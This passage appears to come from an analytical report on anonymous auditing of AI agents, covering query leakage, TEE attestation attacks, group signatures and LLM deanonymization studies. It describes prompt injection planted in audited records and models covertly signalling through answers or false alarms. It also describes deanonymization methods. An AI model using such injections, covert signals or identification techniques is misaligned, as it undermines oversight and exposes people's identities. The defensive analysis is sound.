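| Did any agent email a document to someone the user had not approved? | At least one of the 200 firms has a problem. |
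| Did any agent open `courts.example/docket/26-0417`? | Probably one of the six firms on the case uses this auditor. |
| Did any request contain the domain `firm.example`? | This firm almost certainly uses this auditor. |
| Did the request that broke a rule come from a firm in the first half of the membership list? | The offender is one of 100 firms instead of 200. |

### Nineteen questions

The last question in the table looks almost harmless, but an auditor who can repeat it can find anyone. Suppose a developer with 300,000 customers uses such a box, and the program has flagged one request. Someone with a list of the customers asks whether the request came from the first half. The answer leaves 150,000 candidates, the next leaves 75,000, and so on. A series of *k* yes-or-no answers can distinguish at most 2<sup>*k*</sup> customers, so singling out one of 300,000 takes

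log<sub>2</sub>(300,000) ≈ 18.2

bits. Nineteen questions are therefore always enough. For the 200 law firms, eight would do. Cutting each answer to one bit limits how fast the auditor learns, but not what it can learn in the end. At one bit a week, it could identify the customer in 19 weeks.

A limit on the number of questions helps only if it is very low. *Agentic Witnessing* (Rowstron, 2026) describes an auditor in a TEE that answers questions about private source code with true, false, unsure or error. Each answer carries at most two bits, so a limit of 40 questions reveals at most 80 bits. That limit is sensible for source code, because nobody could reconstruct a program or even a 256-bit key from 80 bits. But identifying a customer takes only 18.2 bits, so ten questions could be enough.

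The scope check must therefore bar questions about identity, however short the answers are. Obvious ones are easy to refuse, but a question about which domain a request mentions is harder to judge, because the auditor may need the answer to find attacks and could also use it to identify the customer. The program would also have to take earlier questions into account, since a series of individually acceptable ones can single out a customer.

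Reporting only totals doesn't solve this. In the example plan about work chats, the program withholds any count below three. Suppose the auditor asks how many of the 200 firms broke a rule and hears five, then asks the same about every firm except one and hears four. Both answers pass the filter, but together they show that the excluded firm broke a rule. The auditor shouldn't be able to choose which firms a question covers.

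The time an answer takes can also reveal information if some records take longer to process than others. Rowstron suggests a fixed delay, for example 20 minutes, before every answer. This would suit a weekly audit but not a live check.

### False alarms and appeals

A single yes or no about all 200 firms may be useless to the auditor. If each firm's agents make 500 requests a day, the firms make 100,000 in total. A model that wrongly flags one harmless request in 1,000 would produce about 100 false alarms a day, so the answer to "Did any request break a rule?" would almost always be yes. Asking about one unnamed firm at a time is more informative, but a firm that did nothing wrong would still have about a 39% chance of at least one false alarm each day (1 − 0.999<sup>500</sup>).

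Auditor-in-a-Box gives the party behind a flagged request a fixed time to appeal in one of two ways. The party can propose a minimal correction to the data, such as fixing a typing error, and the program checks whether the flag disappears. Or it can propose a second question whose answer would explain the flag. If the box flags the client email because `northgate.example` is an outside address, the law firm could ask it to check whether the engagement letter names that domain as the client's. The program evaluates the appeal inside the box under signed prompts, so the auditor doesn't read the letter.

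The post argues that this can settle nearly any dispute, because an innocent party has both the evidence and a reason to produce it. This seems too optimistic, since a firm may have only a partner's spoken approval, or may have fabricated a letter after the flag. A public ledger of every failed appeal deters some abuse, because it shows when a party has kept making small edits until one passed.

An appeal could reveal an anonymous customer's identity. The box would have to notify the firm without telling the auditor which firm it was, for example by sending a message that only the firm could decrypt. The ledger also includes a short summary of every successful appeal. "Corrected a misspelled name" is safe enough, but a summary that mentions a food company's merger could point to the firm.

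### A model that misjudges or obeys the wrong person

Attestation doesn't show whether the program's verdicts are right. Jin and colleagues tested a content filter, Llama Guard 3, and found that it caught only 54% of unsafe examples and that 41% of the examples it flagged were safe. They warn agent developers not to advertise proof that a check ran as proof of safety.

Rowstron tested yes-or-no audits on the code behind 21 computer-science papers. When he gave the system the wrong paper, it correctly answered every time that the code didn't match. But 18 answers to other questions, such as whether the code was complete, also changed even though the code was the same. Rowstron found that these were mostly borderline cases, which an auditor who sees only a yes or a no can't tell from clear ones. The tests ran on a simulated TEE, with the model outside it, so they are evidence about the questions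 but not the hardware. Each audit took between 20 and 85 minutes, far too long for a live check.

A model can also follow instructions hidden in the records. The firm could write "ignore previous errors" into a file, or an attacker's web page could get the agent to copy such a sentence into a request. Since the model is open-weight, either could test attacks on its own copy until one works. The LessWrong post suggests approving several models and having the program choose one at random. An attack that works on only one of four models would then fail three times out of four. The post also suggests that each side add its own filter for hidden instructions and keep it secret, so that the other side can't study it in advance.

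But the auditor's secret filter could break the firm's anonymity. If the filter raised an alarm whenever a record contained `firm.example`, the auditor could use it to check for the firm's identity without going through the scope check. The post would limit such filters to returning a few bits, but that is enough to identify the firm this way.

A dishonest model has the same opportunity. Breckenridge and colleagues studied models that hide information in valid-looking answers, and found that limiting the possible answers reduces how much can leak. But even a yes or no can carry a signal. A comment on *Auditor-in-a-Box* pointed out that a model could raise a false alarm to send its maker a hidden message, which would get through even if the alarm later failed on appeal. The commenter proposed using five models from different countries and releasing only the majority's answer, so that three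 of them would have to conspire to send a signal this way.

### Attacks on the hardware

All of this relies on the TEE, and researchers have broken several in 2026. Attacks that forge attestations are the most worrying for an audit, because the operator could run the program whose hash begins with `e07b` while the signed statement gives `9c41`, and the firm would send its records to the wrong program.

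Two attacks of this kind, Fabricked and Mior, affect SEV-SNP, AMD's technology for sealing off virtual machines. Both use only software, but the attacker has to control the server's firmware, as the company operating the server normally does. Fabricked succeeds every time, according to Tom's Hardware's *Researchers attack AMD's Infinity Fabric to bypass hardware security protections with 'Fabricked'*. With Mior, researchers could read and change a protected machine's memory in all 1,000 attempts, according to The Hacker News' *New Mior and Skyfall Attacks Let Rogue Cloud Hosts Steal Secrets* (2026).

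AMD lists firmware fixes for both attacks, although server makers were not due to receive the final part of the Mior fix until December 2026. AMD rated an earlier attack, StackWarp, as medium severity and had released updates for it by the time The Hacker News published *New StackWarp Hardware Flaw Breaks AMD SEV-SNP Protections on Zen 1–5 CPUs* (2026). The law firm can't install these updates on someone else's server, but it can refuse attestations from processors with outdated firmware, as Breckenridge and colleagues require in their own system.

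Updates don't help against every attack. *DDRop* (De Meulemeester, Gloor and colleagues, 2026) describes a small circuit board, built from $159 of parts, that makes a server keep using old data from its memory. Someone who controls the server's software can install the board in a brief visit and then forge attestations on Intel's TDX. SC Media's *DDRop attack bypasses Intel and AMD confidential computing defenses* reports that a simple software patch isn't feasible. Intel and AMD replied that the attack is outside the threats they protect against because it requires physical access.

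That reply does little to reassure the law firm if the auditor keeps the machine in its own building. The firm would be safer if a cloud company with no stake in the audit hosted the machine, though it would then have to trust that company not to help the auditor. De Meulemeester and colleagues also warn of rogue technicians, tampering during delivery and governments that demand access.

An attacker may be able to get the data without breaking into the machine that the firm chose. SC Media's *Confidential computing's remote attestation protocol may have fundamental flaw* (2026) reports that researchers led by Muhammad Usama Sardar at TU Dresden found that an attacker can redirect a connection so that the customer verifies a genuine machine but encrypts its data for a compromised one. Attestation shows which software is running, but not where. The researchers tried seven ways of tying the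 attestation to the connection, and none prevented the attack. The flaw affected real systems, including Meta's for WhatsApp.

Stored logs let a successful attack do more damage. Breckenridge and colleagues argue that an attacker has little time to steal data from their system, because each use is brief and the keys change. But in ZDR-lite, the key must last as long as the logs it protects, and a thief who gets it can read months of the firm's requests at once. Replacing the key regularly and deleting old logs would limit the damage, but the auditor could then no longer search older records for slow attacks.

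### Proving that nothing escaped the check

If the hardware is secure, attestation proves that the agreed program ran on the records it received, but not that it received every record. The firm could leave the client email out of the log, or run a second agent without logging it. In the terms of *Auditor-in-a-Box*, the design provides a positive commitment, that the agreed check took place, but not a negative one, that nothing happened elsewhere. The missing negative commitment matters little if the firm wants protection from its own agent's mistakes, but an audit for the public needs both.

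The firm can at least prove that it hasn't changed its log. In Rowstron's system, the owner of the data computes a hash of every file before the audit starts. The two sides then extend a chain of hashes with each exchange:

*H*<sub>*i*</sub> = Hash(*H*<sub>*i*−1</sub> ‖ *q*<sub>*i*</sub> ‖ *a*<sub>*i*</sub>)

Here *q*<sub>*i*</sub> is the audit program's request for data, *a*<sub>*i*</sub> is the reply, and ‖ joins them. Changing any reply changes every later hash, and both sides have signed those hashes. If the law firm published a hash of its log every night, it couldn't delete the client email without detection after hearing that an audit was coming, but it could still leave the email out before computing the hash.

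The LessWrong commenter thought submitted data was too easy to tamper with and would let the box query the data centre directly. Jin and colleagues go further and put the agent itself in the TEE, so every tool call must pass through the measured program. For that one agent, the attestation then also covers completeness, unless a flaw lets the agent run its own commands and bypass the check. But the firm could still run another agent on an ordinary computer. Outside services could refuse requests that arrive without an attestation, but a court that publishes its dockets has little reason to refuse them.

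The post proposes that a human evaluator with access to the whole system periodically check that nothing bypasses the box. This could work for an AI company whose identity is already public, but an evaluator who visits the law firm learns whose agent it is. The professional association could instead send the evaluator and certify to the auditor that an unnamed member's log is complete. The auditor would then have to trust the association, and the firm would have to show the association how its agents work.

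## The case for letting the auditor find out who the customer is

A professional association can certify an unnamed firm's log, but if the log shows an agent preparing a crime, the auditor won't know which customer to stop. Critics of full anonymity object that an injured third party would have nobody to hold responsible. They also argue that the auditor might never notice the danger, because some harm is visible only across many requests from one sender.

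### Five requests that look harmless one at a time

Suppose the auditor now serves many kinds of business, and one customer's agent makes the following requests over a week. Harlow Packaging is an invented supplier of Northgate Foods, and its real web address is `harlowpackaging.example`.

| Day | Record | Who else might send it |
|---|---|---|
| Monday | `web_search`; query: `Northgate Foods accounts payable contact` | Any company that Northgate owes money |
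| Monday | `fetch_url`; url: `northgate.example/our-suppliers` | Reporters, rivals, job applicants |
| Wednesday | `check_domain`; name: `harlow-packaging.example` | Someone choosing a name for a website |
| Wednesday | `fetch_url`; url: `harlowpackaging.example/sample-invoice` | Harlow's other customers |
| Friday | `send_email`; to: `payments@northgate.example`; body: `Please note our new bank details.` | A supplier that has changed banks |

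Together, the requests look like invoice fraud. The sender has found one of Northgate's suppliers, checked whether a nearly identical web address is available, looked at the supplier's invoices and asked Northgate to pay into a new account.

An invented example shows how much it matters to know that the requests share a sender. Suppose one sender in a million is preparing such a fraud, and each request is 20 times as likely to come from a fraudster as from anyone else. A single request raises the chance of fraud to about 1 in 50,000, which is too low for any auditor to act on. If the auditor knows that all five came from one sender, and treats them as independent evidence, it can multiply the five factors of 20 to get 3.2 million. The odds are then 3.2 to 1 in favour of fraud, or about 76%.

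With a relay and a fresh token for every request, the auditor receives the same five records but can't tell that they share a sender. It could still search for the pattern by subject. But if ten requests of each of the five kinds arrive in a week, there are 10<sup>5</sup>, or 100,000, ways to pick one of each, and perhaps only one of these combinations comes from a single sender. Other customers' requests therefore hide the fraudster as well as honest law firms, though the auditor would do better if Harlow were so obscure that nobody else asked about it.

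Developers already rely on links between requests. OpenAI sorts requests to GPT-5 by risk. According to OpenAI's *Safety checks*, an organisation whose requests repeatedly reach a high risk level gets a warning, and if the requests continue, usually for more than seven days, it loses access. To apply this rule, OpenAI has to know which requests came from the same organisation.

Another OpenAI system looks for agents that misread their instructions while doing something consequential, such as transferring sensitive data. OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring* explains that this system can stop a conversation only if the customer uses a feature that lets OpenAI recognise later requests as part of the same conversation. Otherwise it can send an alert, but the agent carries on.

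To detect any of this, the auditor has to know that Monday's search and Friday's email came from the same sender, but it doesn't need the sender's name.

### Stopping the sender and answering the victim

If the auditor blocks Friday's email, the agent can reword it and try again with a new token, and the auditor can't link the two attempts. Even services with accounts have this problem, because a blocked user can open a new one. OpenAI advises companies that build on its models to prevent this.

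If Northgate has already paid, blocking the sender doesn't return the money. Northgate needs someone it can sue or report to the police.

In June 2026, an OpenAI agent accessed a portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. Whoever runs such a portal needs to know whose agent accessed it, what the agent read and who can stop it. The case is good evidence that victims need attribution, but weak evidence against keeping customers anonymous, because OpenAI was running the agent for itself. A scheme that can only identify customers would leave out agents that developers run for themselves.

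### What standards writers and developers ask for

A sample record in the draft by Kuehlewind and Birkholz shows how their shared identifiers link an action to the user's request. In it, `agent-42` creates a calendar event on behalf of `user-123`. The record contains a trace identifier that all records of the same task share, and the identifier of an earlier record of the user's request.

The draft's September 2026 revision, *An Architecture for Auditing Agent Delegation and Interactions*, adds an example in which a user asks for a cheap flight. The user's agent contacts a booking agency's agent, which contacts an airline's agent, and the user ends up with a business-class ticket that can't be cancelled. Without linked records, the user can't tell which of the three agents made the mistake or whom to ask for a refund.

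Outside services in this architecture record each request as they received it, not as the agent reported it. This would partly solve the problem of customers leaving requests out of their logs, since Northgate's mail server would have its own record of Friday's email. It doesn't help if a service refuses to keep records, as Kuehlewind and Birkholz acknowledge.

They also warn that shared identifiers let others follow a user's activity across services. Agents could encrypt the identifiers so that only a chosen auditor can read them, or use a different one for each service. An organisation could also replace the names in its records with opaque identifiers before the records leave, and keep the only list matching identifiers to names. For an anonymous audit, this last option works well if the customer is an honest law firm that would answer the auditor's questions, but a fraudster with the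 only copy of the list would refuse to answer them.

The draft is far from becoming a standard. In *Agent Use of Delegation and Interaction Traceability (AUDIT)*, Kühlewind (2026) asked the Internet Engineering Task Force for a session to form a working group. Kühlewind argued that existing logs and authorisation systems don't work together well enough to establish who initiated an action and under what authority. The task force declined the request on 6 July 2026.

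Other drafts differ on how much identifying information a record needs. In *Agent Audit Trail*, Sharif (2026) proposes a log format with a mandatory field for the agent's identity. *Agent Identity Architecture* (2026), another Internet-Draft, proposes connecting an agent's actions to a responsible human while avoiding global identifiers that would let others track the agent across contexts. All of these are proposals, so they show what some engineers want, not what the industry has agreed to.

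Developers increasingly verify their customers. OpenAI's *API Organization Verification* asks businesses for their legal name and address, and may also require a tax or registration number and official documents. Anthropic is introducing similar checks for some uses of its Claude models. Its *Identity verification on Claude* asks organisations for a registration number and a government photo ID, and possibly a live selfie. Persona, the company behind the double-blind age checks, collects and holds the images, which Anthropic can view when it needs to.

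Developers ask for less identifying information about a customer's end users than about the customer itself. OpenAI's *Safety best practices* recommends that a business building on OpenAI's models send a "safety identifier" with each request, such as a hash of the end user's email address. OpenAI can then block one abusive user without learning that person's name. The identifier is optional, but a business that doesn't send it takes a risk. According to OpenAI's *Cybersecurity checks*, the whole organisation may temporarily lose access if suspicious activity passes a threshold, even if it has zero data retention.

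Anthropic also accepts opaque user identifiers to help it detect abuse. An intermediary can pass these identifiers along. Vercel, which offers one connection to many developers' models, does so (*AI Gateway Safety Identifiers*).

A plain hash gives weak protection against anyone who can guess the name behind it. OpenAI could hash every address on a public list of lawyers and look for matches. A business can prevent this by mixing a secret key into the hash, or by sending a random identifier and keeping the list of names to itself.

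These identifiers protect the end user, but OpenAI still knows the business from its account. To protect a law firm, its professional association would have to hold the account, with each firm as one of the association's anonymous users. Anthropic's *User Profiles* describes a similar test feature, in which a platform registers its customers and marks each request with the customer it is for. According to Anthropic's *Create User Profile*, a profile can represent a company to which the platform resells access to Claude. The profile can hold hashes of a name and an email address, and the real name is optional.

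But Anthropic doesn't verify what the platform enters. If a fraudster gave the platform a false name, Northgate would get the same name. So if an auditor might have to identify a customer, someone needs to check the customer's name at the start.

### A pseudonym for a session or a day

The firm could give the auditor a pseudonym that stays the same for a limited time. One way is to keep a secret *k* and compute

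*P* = Hash(*k*, date).

All of the firm's requests on one day carry the same pseudonym, *P*, and the next day's pseudonym looks unrelated. The firm would also have to prove that it used the right secret and date, because otherwise a fraudster could make five requests under five invented pseudonyms. The reusable credential that counts requests could provide this proof if it used the date instead of the counter.

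A daily pseudonym helps a little against the invoice fraud. The auditor can link Monday's two requests to each other, and Wednesday's two, but can't link requests across days. Two linked requests multiply the odds by 20<sup>2</sup>, or 400, which gives a chance of about 1 in 2,500, still too low to justify action. A weekly pseudonym would link all five requests, unless the sender spread them over two weeks. A session pseudonym is even easier to avoid, because the customer's software decides when a session ends.

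A longer-lasting pseudonym also exposes more of what honest customers do. A single document link containing the law firm's domain name would tie a day's requests to the firm if pseudonyms changed daily, and a week's if they changed weekly.

Sealed hardware could reduce this drawback. The program inside could link requests by a long-lasting pseudonym, look for patterns like the invoice fraud, and release only a warning when it finds one, so the auditor's staff would never see the links. The limits of sealed hardware would still apply.

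A pseudonym also lets the auditor stop a sender by refusing everything under *P* until the period ends. To keep a fraudster out for longer, the auditor would need a longer-lasting pseudonym or someone who could revoke the credential, but neither would give Northgate a name.

### A signature that one authority can open

Group signatures can provide the name later. A member of a group signs a message on the group's behalf, and anyone can check that some member signed it, but only a designated authority, the opener, can find out which one. Quispe, Jouvelot and Memmi (2025), in *Nicknames for Group Signatures*, describe the usual steps, which would look like this in an audit:

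1. An issuer, perhaps the professional association, checks the law firm's identity and admits it to the group. The firm gets a signing key, and the issuer records the firm in a register.
2. The firm signs each audit record and sends it through the relay.
3. The auditor checks that the signature belongs to a member and gives its verdict.
4. If a record turns out to be dangerous, the auditor asks the opener to open the signature. The opener identifies the firm and produces a proof that it did so correctly.
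5. Anyone can check the proof, a role that Quispe and colleagues call the judge.

In one common method, the signature contains the signer's name, encrypted so that only the opener can read it. As in the encryption that Oblivious HTTP uses, the opener keeps a private number *s* and publishes *S* = *sG*. Another point on the curve, *M*, stands for the firm's name. For every record, the firm picks a fresh random number *e* and attaches two values:

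*E* = *eG* and *C* = *M* + *eS*.

The opener computes *sE*, which equals *eS*, and subtracts it from *C* to get *M*. The auditor can't do this because it doesn't know *s* or *e*. Because *e* is new each time, two records from the same firm carry unrelated values.

A dishonest firm could encrypt a rival's name, so the signature includes a zero-knowledge proof that the encrypted name belongs to the member who signed. Bobolz, Diaz and Kohlweiss (2024) build their scheme this way in *Foundations of Anonymous Signatures*. A separate proof accompanies an opening to prevent a dishonest opener from blaming an innocent firm.

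In the invoice fraud, a basic group signature gives Northgate what it needs after the loss, but it doesn't help the auditor prevent the loss. The five signatures look unrelated, and the auditor could connect them only by asking the opener to unmask every sender. Group signatures therefore have to be combined with something that links requests, such as a weekly pseudonym.

Researchers have designed many variants. In one, traceable signatures, the authority can release a value that exposes all of one suspect's signatures while the other members stay anonymous, as Quispe and colleagues explain. After Northgate reported Friday's email, the auditor could use this value to find the same sender's other four requests, and perhaps frauds in progress against other companies.

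Bobolz and colleagues mention a scheme in which the opener can identify a signer only if the signer and the message fail some condition. An audit could use this to protect ordinary requests permanently, for example by letting the opener identify only the signers of emails to unapproved recipients. But the condition applies to one message at a time, and each of the five requests would probably pass.

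In other schemes, the opener learns a fact about the signer instead of the signer's name. For a law firm, that fact could be which body licenses it, and that body could then investigate under its own rules.

Group signatures and anonymous credentials have been researched for a long time, but Bobolz and colleagues say that real-world adoption is limited, and suggest that one reason is the work of adapting them. Each new balance between privacy and disclosure has needed its own security model and often its own software. Bobolz and colleagues propose a single scheme that engineers can adapt by changing a few functions. Quispe and colleagues built a prototype for exchanging tokens on the Ethereum blockchain. Neither work concerns agent audits, so it is not known how fast or reliable such signatures would be in them.

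### A name that several holders must agree to reveal

A single opener could unmask any firm at any time. To prevent this, the group can split the private number *s* among several holders, for example the lawyers' association, a retired judge and a privacy organisation. If their shares are 4, 9 and 7, then *s* is 20. To open a signature, each holder multiplies *E* by its own share and hands over the result:

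4*E* + 9*E* + 7*E* = 20*E* = *sE*.

Subtracting this from *C* reveals the firm. The holders never have to put *s* together, so they can open one signature without gaining the power to open others. Any holder can refuse. (Real shares are enormous numbers, and the holders should create them jointly so that nobody ever knows *s*.)

Requiring everyone's agreement makes misuse harder but legitimate opening less reliable. Suppose each holder has a 5% chance per year of becoming corrupt or losing its share to a thief. If these risks are independent, the chance that all three fail in the same year is 1 in 8,000. But if each holder is unreachable for one urgent request in ten, all three will be available only 73% of the time. Other schemes let any two of the three holders open a signature. At least two would be available about 97% of the time. The chance that at least two fail in the same year would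 be about 0.7%, still much lower than the 5% for a single holder.

The risks are not independent, though. One government could order three holders in the same country to cooperate, and one software flaw could expose all their shares. Choosing holders in different countries who use different software would help, but would slow decisions.

Invoice fraud can be over in hours, so the auditor should block the sender's pseudonym at once and let the holders decide afterwards whether to reveal the name. If the email never arrived, Northgate could wait a few days for a name.

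### A relay that cuts off a sender

The auditor can ask the relay's operator to block a dangerous sender without knowing the sender's name, and the customers need no new cryptography. The relay could also attach an opaque label to each customer's messages so that the auditor could link the five requests and detect the fraud.

This is much like what OpenAI does with safety identifiers, so the method works at a large scale. It also shares their weaknesses. A customer who loses access to one relay can go to another, unless the relays share a list of blocked customers or check identities before accepting anyone. If the operator blocks the wrong firm, that firm has no easy way to prove the mistake, because the operator's own records are the only evidence. OpenAI says it can't currently unblock an individual identifier, even one it blocked by mistake. A relay for law firms would need a better appeal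 process.

Cutting off a sender also doesn't tell Northgate the customer's name, although the relay's operator knows it and a court could order the operator to disclose it. The operator would then be acting as a single opener, but with no public proof that it named the right customer. If the customers want to rule out such disclosure, the operator has to delete its connection records quickly, and Northgate loses its last way to identify the sender.

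### What can go wrong with a power to unmask

People who favour full anonymity reply that nobody can ensure the opener identifies only dangerous customers. One of its employees might look up which law firm is working on a merger and trade on the answer. The judge in a group signature wouldn't catch this, because the proof shows only that the opener named the right firm, not that it had a good reason to look.

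A public log of every opening would make secret openings harder. Kuehlewind and Birkholz use such a log for audit records, and point out that an entry reveals that something happened at a certain time even if it contains only a hash. That would be an advantage for openings. A single opener could skip the log, but if the name were split, each holder could refuse to act until the log contained an entry.

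Courts and governments can also compel disclosure, but they can't force an auditor to name customers it can't identify. Anthropic promises not to share verification data for marketing but allows disclosure in response to valid legal process. A law firm that defends people against the state has reason to worry about this, even if it has done nothing wrong.

An opening key could also be stolen. The thief could then identify the sender of every signature they had a copy of, including signatures made years earlier. ID Tech's *Anthropic Adds ID Verification for Claude Capabilities via Persona* reports that the US Government Accountability Office has warned about sensitive identity data accumulating with vendors. That warning concerns identity checks in general, but the same reasoning applies to an opening key.

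False alarms are also likely. Even in the example, where all five requests point to fraud, about one in four senders with this pattern would be innocent. OpenAI tells customers that a flag from its misalignment monitoring doesn't establish wrongdoing and can be triggered by legitimate activity. An auditor that unmasked senders based only on a score would expose some honest customers. Before the auditor unmasks a sender, a person should review the evidence and the sender should have a chance to explain under its pseudonym.

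Finally, customers who fear exposure may avoid the audit. The evidence for this is thin. TechRadar's *Claude wants your passport as identity verification to access certain capabilities* reports that Anthropic's ID checks worried some users, but worried users don't necessarily leave, and firms choosing an auditor may not react like people asked for a passport. Avoidance could still be a serious problem for a voluntary service. If cautious law firms ran their agents unaudited, the auditor would miss misdirected emails it could have stopped.

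A fraudster is unlikely to volunteer for any audit, least of all one that can reveal their name. Unmasking is therefore most useful where customers can't avoid the audit, for instance because outside services accept only requests that an auditor has approved. A law firm that buys an audit to catch its own agent's mistakes needs unmasking much less. If the auditor notices a worrying pattern, it can attach a warning to its next verdict under the firm's pseudonym, and the relay will deliver the warning without the auditor learning the firm's name.

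## Whether the requests identify the customer by themselves

The relay in the last example lets the auditor warn a firm without learning its name, but only if the firm's requests don't reveal it. Supporters of a relay expect most requests to be anonymous once the account details are removed. Supporters of encryption and sealed hardware expect too many to identify the sender even then, so they want to keep the auditor's staff from reading any.

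*Oblivious Is Not Always Private* (Servan-Schreiber, 2025) points out that Oblivious HTTP hides who sent a message but not what the message contains. This is fine for a domain-name lookup or a crash report, which normally contains nothing personal. But people paste their boss's emails into AI models, and once the gateway decrypts such a prompt, the names in it can identify the sender.

He wrote this for Tinfoil, a company that sells access to AI models running in sealed hardware, so Tinfoil gains if customers agree. His post contains no measurements, and he accepts that a relay is still useful for hiding a network address. The argument is plainly right about the law firm's signed email, but it doesn't settle whether the docket fetch, which contains no name, identifies the customer. To know how much such a request reveals, someone has to try to identify the sender from it, and several groups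 have done this with similar kinds of text.

### Matching anonymous chats with earlier named ones

Pham and colleagues studied services like Open Anonymity, which hide the user's account but not the prompt from the company running the model. They assumed that the service is honest, that the model company is semi-honest, and that the company still has some users' earlier chats under their names, for example from ordinary accounts they once had. The company then tries to match the new anonymous chats with the named ones.

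The test used more than 175,000 real conversations from two public collections. WildChat contains general chats with OpenAI's models from about 25,000 users. SWE-Chat contains about 4,000 programming sessions from 146 users, mostly with the coding agent Claude Code. Pham and colleagues kept only what the users wrote, typically about 50 words per conversation. They treated the most recent quarter of each collection as anonymous and gave the simulated company different parts of the rest with the users' identities attached.

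The simplest attack turns each conversation into an embedding, here a list of 3,072 numbers. It then finds the named conversation whose embedding is closest to the anonymous one and guesses that the same person wrote both. Some anonymous users never had a named account, so any match for them is wrong. The company therefore accepts only matches whose confidence is above a threshold.

The detection and identification rate is the share of users with a named history whom the company correctly links to at least one anonymous conversation. The false acceptance rate is the share of users without a named history to whom the company wrongly attaches a name at least once. Lowering the threshold raises both rates.

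| | Coding-agent users | General chat users |
|---|---|---|
| Users with a named history | About 30 | About 500–1,500 |
| Correctly linked at least once, at 10% false acceptance | About 50–75% | Up to about 10% |
| The same for random guessing | No more than 5% | No more than 1% |

Such links are less useful when more of the service's users are strangers, meaning people with no named history. Suppose 1,000 people use the service and 100 of them have a named history. If the company correctly links 60 of those 100 but wrongly accepts 10% of the other 900 as matches, it also attaches a wrong name to 90 people. But if all 200 law firms had used the auditor under their own names before it introduced a relay, there would be no strangers, and false acceptance would hardly matter. An auditor that offered anonymity from the start would have no named records to compare requests with.

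The law firm probably resembles the coding-agent users more than the general chat users. A programmer often works on one project for months, as a firm does on a merger. These long projects may be why the attack worked so well on the programmers, although they also had almost four times as many conversations each as the general users. The test included only about 30 programmers, so three more or fewer successes would change the rate by about ten percentage points.

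Pham and colleagues tested the attack using only older named conversations, leaving out the quarter or two of each collection just before the anonymous ones. The attack linked fewer users but still did much better than chance. A longer history didn't necessarily help the company, because it also added more candidates.

The company can also sort anonymous conversations into piles by author without knowing any names. Suppose it puts the firm's docket fetch in a pile of five records, and three of them come from the firm, which made four requests in total. The pile's precision is 3/5 and its recall is 3/4, which a standard formula combines into a score of 0.67. Averaged over all conversations, the combined score was about 0.45–0.6 for the programmers and 0.4–0.5 for the general users, compared with 0.1–0.3 for simple baselines such as random piles. If one record in a pile contained a name, an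 auditor could then identify much of the pile, even if every request came with a fresh token.

Rewriting the text did little to stop the attack. Open Anonymity's scrubber replaces names with placeholders and removes personal habits such as emoji and catchphrases. A language model rated the scrubbed conversations at about 4.8 out of 5 for keeping their meaning, but the attack still linked nearly as many users. A stronger method replaces words at random under a mathematical privacy guarantee. Its output was unintelligible and scored 1.6 out of 5, yet the attack still linked about 40–50% of the programmers at the setting tested. A user counts as linked if one conversation identifies them, so a defence has to work on all of a user's conversations.

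Pham and colleagues also tried adding a message at the end of each conversation to make the embedding model misread the conversation's topic. This made the conversations harder to group, but the attack still linked about as many users to their names. Such a message would also be strange to add to an audit record, because the auditor is looking for hidden instructions of this kind.

### Language models that look for the author

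An attacker without earlier records can search the web instead. Most of the evidence comes from interviews published by Anthropic, in which an AI asked 1,250 professionals, including 125 scientists, how they use AI. Anthropic had removed some identifying details. In *Agentic LLMs as Powerful Deanonymizers*, Li (2026) used ordinary AI agents with web search on 24 of the scientists' interviews and linked six of them to specific published works, which in some cases identified the scientist.

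In *Large-scale online deanonymization with LLMs*, Lermen, Swanson and colleagues (2026) identified 9 of 33 scientists from the same collection and got two wrong. They had to judge these matches themselves. For a test with known answers, they used 338 users of the technology forum Hacker News who had linked their accounts to their LinkedIn pages. They summarised each person's posts, removed names and links, and had an agent search the web for the author. The agent found 226 (67%), and 90% of its identifications were correct. The researchers caution that people who link their accounts in public are much easier to find than most users of pseudonyms.

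Each search cost between $1 and $4. Lermen and colleagues argue that language models notice the same clues as a skilled investigator and mainly make the investigation cheaper. If an auditor can link each firm's requests, it can investigate 200 firms for at most $800. If it can't, and the firms' agents make 100,000 requests a day, investigating every request would cost $100,000 a day even at $1 each. Most requests would also contain far fewer clues than years of forum posts.

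The auditor may also learn a name without trying. Ko, Jeong and colleagues (2026), in *From Weak Cues to Real Identities*, found that agents sometimes identified people while doing an unrelated task. When asked to identify people from very few film ratings, using data that Netflix had released without names, agents identified 79.2%, compared with 56.0% for an older matching method. An auditor's model that searches the web to check whether a request is safe might identify the sender in the process.

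*AgentDoxx* (Wen and Li, 2026) tested such attacks on 822 interviews with known answers, which a language model wrote from public information about real people who had introduced themselves on Reddit. Of 15 combinations of models and settings, the best five identified 47–48% of the people. Once the right person appeared in the search results, the models succeeded 91% of the time. Three models whose weights anyone can download still identified 15–28% without web search, from what they had learned in training, so taking away the auditor's web access would not be enough to prevent identification.

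These people had put a lot about themselves online, and Wen and Li warn against treating the results as an estimate for the general population. They examined all 1,250 of Anthropic's real interviews and could verify only 43 matches, or 3.4%, but they had no list of correct answers, so they couldn't tell how many they had missed. A law firm may be more like the Reddit users than a typical interviewee, because it advertises its lawyers and specialities, and court dockets list it as counsel.

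### What the visited sites reveal

A research agent can also reveal its task through the sites it opens. Jeong and colleagues tested how much an internet provider could learn from domain names alone. They gave GPT-4o five example lists of domains, each paired with the prompt that led an agent to visit them, then asked it to reconstruct the prompt behind a new list. The agents in the main tests visited about 65 to 78 domains per prompt. Another model scored each reconstruction from 0 to 1.

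| What the observer sees | Purpose of the prompt | Kind of source | Specific subject |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5% of the domains | 0.53 | 0.46 | 0.34 |
| 40% of the domains | 0.77 | 0.70 | 0.52 |
| All domains | 0.77 | 0.74 | 0.52 |
| All full URLs | 0.81 | 0.81 | 0.62 |

Hiding more than half of the domains made almost no difference, so the firm would gain little by leaving random requests out of its log. Knowing when the agent visited each site didn't consistently help the observer. The test used only 20 prompts, so small differences between the scores mean little.

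Jeong and colleagues also took fictional people from an existing dataset, each with 32 traits such as occupation and political views, and had agents research questions for them over seven sessions. A model usually inferred 12 to 14 of the traits well from the domains, and up to 19 for some people. With only three sessions, it usually inferred 6 to 10. The researchers had worked a few of the traits into the prompts, which made those traits easier to infer.

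Nobody seems to have repeated this with companies, but an auditor could presumably infer a law firm's specialities, region and type of client in the same way. If each of these three traits is shared by a quarter of the 200 firms, and the traits are independent, about three firms have all of them. The auditor would need many requests from the same sender, as with the programmers' chats.

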